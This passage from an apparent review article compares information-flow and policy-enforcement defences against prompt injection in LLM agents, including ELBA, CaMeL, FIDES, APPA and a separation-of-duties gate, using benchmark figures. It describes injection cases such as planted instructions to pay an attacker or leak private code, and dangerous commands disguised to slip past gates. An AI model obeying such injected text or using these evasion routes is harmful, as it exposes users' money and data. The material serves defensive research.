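LLMbda's proofs also cover its interpreter, so a reviewer doesn't have to search the interpreter for a missed label. The reviewer still has to trust Lean's proof checker, the compiler that turns the interpreter into machine code, the operating system and the hardware.

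For the payments company, a verified type checker and monitor would greatly strengthen two of the eight layers but leave the other six unchanged. A proof that OpenAI's sandboxes could contact only the package service would not have prevented the July intrusion, because the agents reached the internet through that service.

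## How much useful work does enforcement cost?

Every mechanism described so far also stops some harmless work. Researchers usually measure that loss on AgentDojo, a 2024 benchmark that simulates an office workspace, a travel service, a bank and a Slack team chat. It contains 97 user tasks and 36 injection tasks.

A user task is an ordinary request, such as summarising recent bank transactions. An injection task is an attacker's goal, such as transferring money to the attacker. The benchmark stages an attack by pairing a user task with an injection task and planting the attacker's text in data the agent will read. After the run, ordinary code checks whether the agent met the user's goal and whether it met the attacker's. Utility is the share of user tasks completed, and security is the share of injections resisted. An agent that did nothing would score 0% for utility and 100% for security,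 so neither score is very informative without the other.

Scores from different suites aren't comparable, because some require an agent to act on untrusted text much more often than others. When Costa and colleagues applied their policies to the simplest kind of agent, it completed 73% of the travel tasks but only 20% of the Slack tasks.

### ELBA and CaMeL on the Slack tasks

Zhou and colleagues ran ELBA and CaMeL on the same 21 Slack tasks with three models from Anthropic and one from OpenAI. With no attack, the systems completed this many tasks:

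| Model | ELBA, policies on | CaMeL, policies on | ELBA, policies off | CaMeL, policies off |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 10 | 5 | 18 | 15 |
| Opus 4.8 | 9 | 6 | 16 | 16 |
| GPT 5.4 | 10 | 5 | 16 | 17 |
| Sonnet 5 | 8 | 4 | 14 | 13 |

ELBA completed 6 to 8 fewer tasks with the policies on than with them off, and CaMeL completed 9 to 12 fewer. With the policies off, the two systems completed about the same number of tasks, and the 95% confidence interval for the difference included zero for every model.

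With policies on, 21 tasks are too few to measure ELBA's lead over CaMeL precisely. The interval for that lead ran from 3 to 42 percentage points with GPT 5.4, and from -7 (CaMeL ahead) to 34 with Opus 4.8. The 105 attacked runs (21 user tasks times 5 injection tasks) give a clearer result. Across three styles of attack, ELBA completed the user task in 40 to 52 runs and CaMeL in 22 to 30. For the most direct style, the lower ends of the four intervals were 8 to 17 points in ELBA's favour. However, these runs reuse the same 21 user tasks, so the intervals probably understate the uncertainty.

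The comparison also doesn't isolate the effect of ELBA's design, because the two systems enforced different policies. Zhou and colleagues wrote a new policy for ELBA and suggest standardising policies in future comparisons.

ELBA took about three times as long as CaMeL in total, mainly because its agents call the model again after reading data, whereas CaMeL writes one program at the start. The type checker accounts for little of the extra time. ELBA spent 3.4% of its time on programs that had failed the check, and in 0.26% of runs the model never produced a valid program.

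### Why every standard attack failed

Both systems resisted all 105 injections with every model and every style of attack, even with policies off. CaMeL still keeps its models separate when its policies are off, but ELBA has no comparable barrier without policies. ELBA's sub-agents did not obey the attackers' text, although they read it and could have done so.

AgentDojo's attacks come from fixed templates, and recent models recognise or ignore them. *APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) leaves the benchmark out of its evaluation for this reason. If an undefended agent already resists every attack, a defence can't improve on it. The paper also objects that AgentDojo's tasks are short and end once the agent has acted, so the benchmark doesn't show whether a refusal ruins later work.

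This doesn't mean the models are safe from injection. Zhou and colleagues point out that GPT-Red, OpenAI's automated attack system, consistently got past GPT-5.5's defences. An attacker that adapts to a model is a much harder test than a template from 2024. AgentDojo can still measure how much useful work a policy prevents, but with current models it is a poor measure of how much harm the policy prevents.

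### When the sub-agent is forced to obey

Zhou and colleagues measured the harm with the worst-case test, in which they replaced a sub-agent's prompt with the attacker's text. They ran each of the 105 pairs seven times with each model, for 735 runs per setting.

| Model | Resisted, policies on | Tasks completed, policies on | Resisted, policies off | Tasks completed, policies off |
|---|---|---|---|---|
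| Opus 4.7 | 100% | 47.8% | 57.8% | 71.2% |
| Opus 4.8 | 100% | 42.4% | 62.6% | 75.8% |
| GPT 5.4 | 100% | 46.0% | 84.5% | 75.9% |
| Sonnet 5 | 100% | 40.0% | 73.5% | 67.2% |

Of the 2,940 runs with policies on, AgentDojo's scoring counted 29 as successful attacks because the agent had opened a certain web address. Zhou and colleagues reviewed all 29 and found that no data had leaked.

With policies on, ELBA completed 40 to 48% of tasks under this attack, compared with 38 to 48% without an attack. A fully compromised sub-agent added almost nothing to the loss the policies had already caused. Zhou and colleagues didn't run this test on CaMeL, so we can't tell from it which system does better in the worst case.

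### Banking tasks and the two attacks that succeeded

Garby and colleagues tested RANDORI, their agent written in LLMbda, on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks with three models. They reran CaMeL on the same tasks with two of those models. Each agent attempted each task three times, so the maximum score was 48.

| Agent | GPT-5.2 | Qwen3.7-plus | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| RANDORI, labels enforced | 36 | 36 | 31 |
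| CaMeL, policy checks off | 32 | not run | 34 |
| CaMeL, policy checks on | 18 | not run | 18 |

The policy checks roughly halved the number of tasks CaMeL completed. With its labels on, RANDORI did about as well as CaMeL without checks, within wide margins of error. But RANDORI enforces only a subset of CaMeL's policies, and its planner may endorse untrusted data, so part of its advantage over CaMeL with checks comes from permitting more.

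RANDORI resisted all but 2 of the 1,296 attacks. In both failures, which involved GPT-5.2, it made a payment specified in a file that the attacker had rewritten. A label records that the payment details came from an untrusted file, but it can't show whether they are genuine. If the agent hadn't endorsed the file, the labels would have blocked the payment, but they would also have blocked every legitimate request of the same kind.

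According to Garby and colleagues, the original evaluation of CaMeL recorded two successful attacks. One was the same payment from a file, which CaMeL's designers consider outside the threats it defends against. In the other, the agent quoted hotel reviews word for word, and AgentDojo's scoring counted the quotation as a successful attack. The same scoring problem caused TACIT's only recorded failure in 1,926 AgentDojo trials.

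In the reruns of CaMeL, 5 of the 622 attacks that ran to completion succeeded with the policy checks off, and none of 588 did with them on. On this benchmark, the checks prevented less than 1% of attacks and reduced useful work by nearly half. They would look better against a stronger attacker, as ELBA did in the worst-case test.

### FIDES and the two sources of lost work

The FIDES results date from 2025 and come from tests on older OpenAI models, which were easier to attack. With GPT-4o, 152 injections succeeded against an ordinary agent, 21 against FIDES with its policies off, and none against FIDES with its policies on. The zero is partly due to how Costa and colleagues labelled the data. They marked a field as untrusted if at least one of AgentDojo's attacks used it, but a company labelling its own data doesn't know in advance which fields an attacker will use.

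With no attack, GPT-4o completed these shares of the tasks:

| Agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary, policies off | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary, policies on | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, policies off | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% |
| FIDES, policies on | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

FIDES loses useful work in two ways. Hiding untrusted data in variables makes the job harder for the model, which lowered the Slack score from 93.3% to 63.8% before any policies were applied. The policies then block some actions, which lowered the score to 47.6%. With policies on, FIDES still did better than the ordinary agent everywhere except travel, where many tasks need only tools that the policy allows after the agent has read untrusted text.

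Some refusals followed directly from the policy. Many banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, which the policy is meant to prevent. In other cases GPT-4o made mistakes. It confused the names of variables, and in one Slack task it requested a list of channels it didn't need, which tainted the conversation and blocked a step the task needed. A better model makes fewer such mistakes. With o1, a reasoning model, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks instead of 41%. The refusals that follow from the policy will remain with any model unless the policy changes.

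### What separating duties costs

AgentDojo starts from text written to mislead a model. *Separation of Duties for Privileged LLM Agents* (Jing, 2026) starts one step later, with an agent that has already decided to run a dangerous command. In Jing's design, a planner proposes an action, a policy gate allows or refuses it, an executor carries out allowed actions, and an auditor reviews the log. Jing's benchmark includes 54 harmless operations and 117 workable attempts to disguise a dangerous command, for example by writing a file path in an unusual form.

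| Configuration | Disguised commands that got through | Harmless operations refused |
|---|---|---|
| Direct execution | 98.3% | 0% |
| Gate that checks the command's text | 43.6% | 0% |
| All four roles | 30.8% | 0% |
| All four roles and an operating-system sandbox | 7.7% | 11.1% |

The sandbox accounts for the last large gain and for every refusal of harmless work. The 11.1% is 6 of 54 operations, so the true rate could plausibly be between 5% and 22%. Jing traces the refusals to a mismatch between two lists of where writing is permitted. The gate allows writes to the workspace and the temporary folder, but the sandbox allows them only in the current session's folder. Aligning the lists might recover some of the refused work.

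Jing calculated the last row with a model of the sandbox, then checked the model by running the attacks that could test it on the real sandbox. A similar share succeeded (5 of 66), but the model and the real sandbox often disagreed on individual cases. In a separate comparison, the real sandbox blocked 45 of 88 attacks that ran without it. It also let one attack silently delete a file on another disk volume, which was impossible in the model.

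When the executor checked that the file it was about to run still matched the approved version, it blocked 90.3% of attacks on the approval process, up from 61.3%, and refused no additional harmless operations. The delay was also small after Jing fixed a slow search. Finding a recent approval in a log of 50,000 entries then took less than 1 millisecond, down from 164 milliseconds.

For comparison, Jing gave three current models a prompt telling them to seek approval before anything dangerous. The models let through between 53 and 59 of 59 disguised commands and stopped at most 1 of 30 harmless operations. In these figures, a request for approval counts as permission, assuming that an agent working alone would approve its own request. The prompt would have done better with a careful person answering the requests.

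### Recovering the lost work

Enforcement blocks less useful work if a person can overrule a refusal. Prudentia, which Kolluri and colleagues (2026) built on FIDES, shows the model the labels and policies so that it can plan actions they allow. If the model still needs something the policy forbids, it can ask the user to endorse a piece of data or approve a single action.

Microsoft's *Information-flow control* gives an example where such a question is necessary. Alex asks an agent to answer his email. Priya has sent him a preview of the quarterly sales, and Marco has written to ask about them. Only Alex may read both messages, so only he may read a reply that draws on both.

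The agent therefore has to ask Alex before it answers Marco, and it can name Marco as the new reader of the data. If Priya had copied Marco on her message, he would be a permitted reader and the agent could answer without asking.

Finer policies cause fewer refusals. In Microsoft's coding example, an attacker posts an issue in a public repository with instructions for the agent to publish code from a private one. The policy blocks public posts only after the agent has read both untrusted text and private data. An agent that works only in public repositories, or only in private ones, never triggers it.

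#### Refusals that list a way forward

APPA, the system by Kravchenko and colleagues, returns possible remedies with each refusal. The agent may be able to complete a missing earlier step, get approval for that exact call, or pass the data through a trusted program that removes the sensitive parts. It can also read the data in a temporary copy of the conversation, which returns only narrow values such as a number or a choice from a fixed list.

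Kravchenko and colleagues prove that an agent can't clear a label-based refusal by reading more data, because each new item either leaves the conversation's label unchanged or makes it more restrictive. APPA therefore searches the developer's registered remedies for a sequence that clears the refusal, and always finds one if it exists.

Suppose a support agent has to read a public web page before updating an internal database. If the main conversation read the page directly, its label would change and block the update. Instead, a temporary copy of the conversation reads the page and returns a ticket number, a severity and a component name. If the developer has decided to trust values of those types, the main conversation keeps its label and the update goes ahead. An attacker who controls the page can still choose a false severity.

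Kravchenko and colleagues tested APPA with three models on Bench-Corp, a set of 20 long office tasks. APPA completed 88 to 90% of the runs, and no attack succeeded in any of its 600 runs. Without enforcement, agents completed 90 to 92.5% of the runs, but attacks succeeded in 30 to 39.5%. Enforcement therefore lowered the completion rate by only a few percentage points.

The recovery features restored more than half of the work without weakening the protection. With GPT-5.6 Luna, completion fell from 88% to 56.5% without the temporary copies, and to 35% without the suggested remedies. No attack succeeded in either case.

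Bench-Corp concentrates on situations APPA was built to handle, and the runs repeat only 20 task designs. APPA did much worse on the poisoned-memory tasks in another benchmark, AgentThreatBench. Across the three models under normal prompting, it completed 71 of 150 runs, while a version of FIDES completed all 150. That version did so by leaving the path from memory to the user unguarded, and 103 of 150 attacks on it succeeded under more aggressive prompting.

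### Is a conservative filter worth its refusals?

Zhou and colleagues argue that a strict filter is useful even if it often refuses harmless actions, because it never passes an action that violates its policy. Following Kolluri and colleagues, they propose using the filter to decide which actions a person must review. If an agent attempts 1,000 consequential actions a week and 100 fail the label check, a person reviews 100 requests instead of 1,000. On this view, the fair comparison is with an agent that needs approval for every consequential action.

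The filter can also be worth its cost when it simply refuses. If refusals cost the payments company $500 a week in staff time, or $26,000 a year, the filter would pay for itself by preventing one $500,000 theft every 19 years.

The opposing argument is that users meet the refusals every day but may never notice an attack. A user who turned off ELBA's policies in the Slack comparison would have gained 6 to 8 tasks out of 21, and still no standard attack would have succeeded. Such a user has good reason to turn the policies off, and may learn why they were there only after a successful attack. None of these studies observed people using such a filter over time, so they can't show how many would disable it.

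Sending every refusal to a person doesn't remove this problem. Microsoft warns that constant approval requests scale poorly and make people less vigilant, and a person who approves everything has in effect switched the filter off. People are most likely to keep the filter on if it covers only actions that could do serious harm and if a refusal usually leads to another way of finishing the task. APPA's results suggest that the second condition can be met, at least for tasks where a developer can list the remedies in advance.

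### What developers have shipped

Ordinary products already include coarse controls. Claude Code combines an operating-system sandbox with permission rules, and Anthropic and Docker document spending limits. In December 2025, Google described a control for agents in its Chrome browser. Zhou and colleagues summarise it as limiting the websites that an agent can read or change. StrongDM says it uses hidden test scenarios in its own software development.

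Released software offers label tracking mainly as an option. In an undated post, Microsoft says that GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent for the terminal, has experimental support that a user turns on with a flag. So far, it enforces policies for only some tools from GitHub's own server. That server can label files and issues from public repositories as untrusted, but only if the developer requests the labels. Microsoft's Agent Framework, a library for building agents, includes a security module that the developer has to configure. The module hides untrusted data in variables and either blocks a violation or asks a person.

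Microsoft has published a gateway, a program that sits between an agent and existing tools and adds the labels. For each tool it covers, a developer must describe the structure of the tool's output, write a function that calculates the output's labels, and write or choose a policy.
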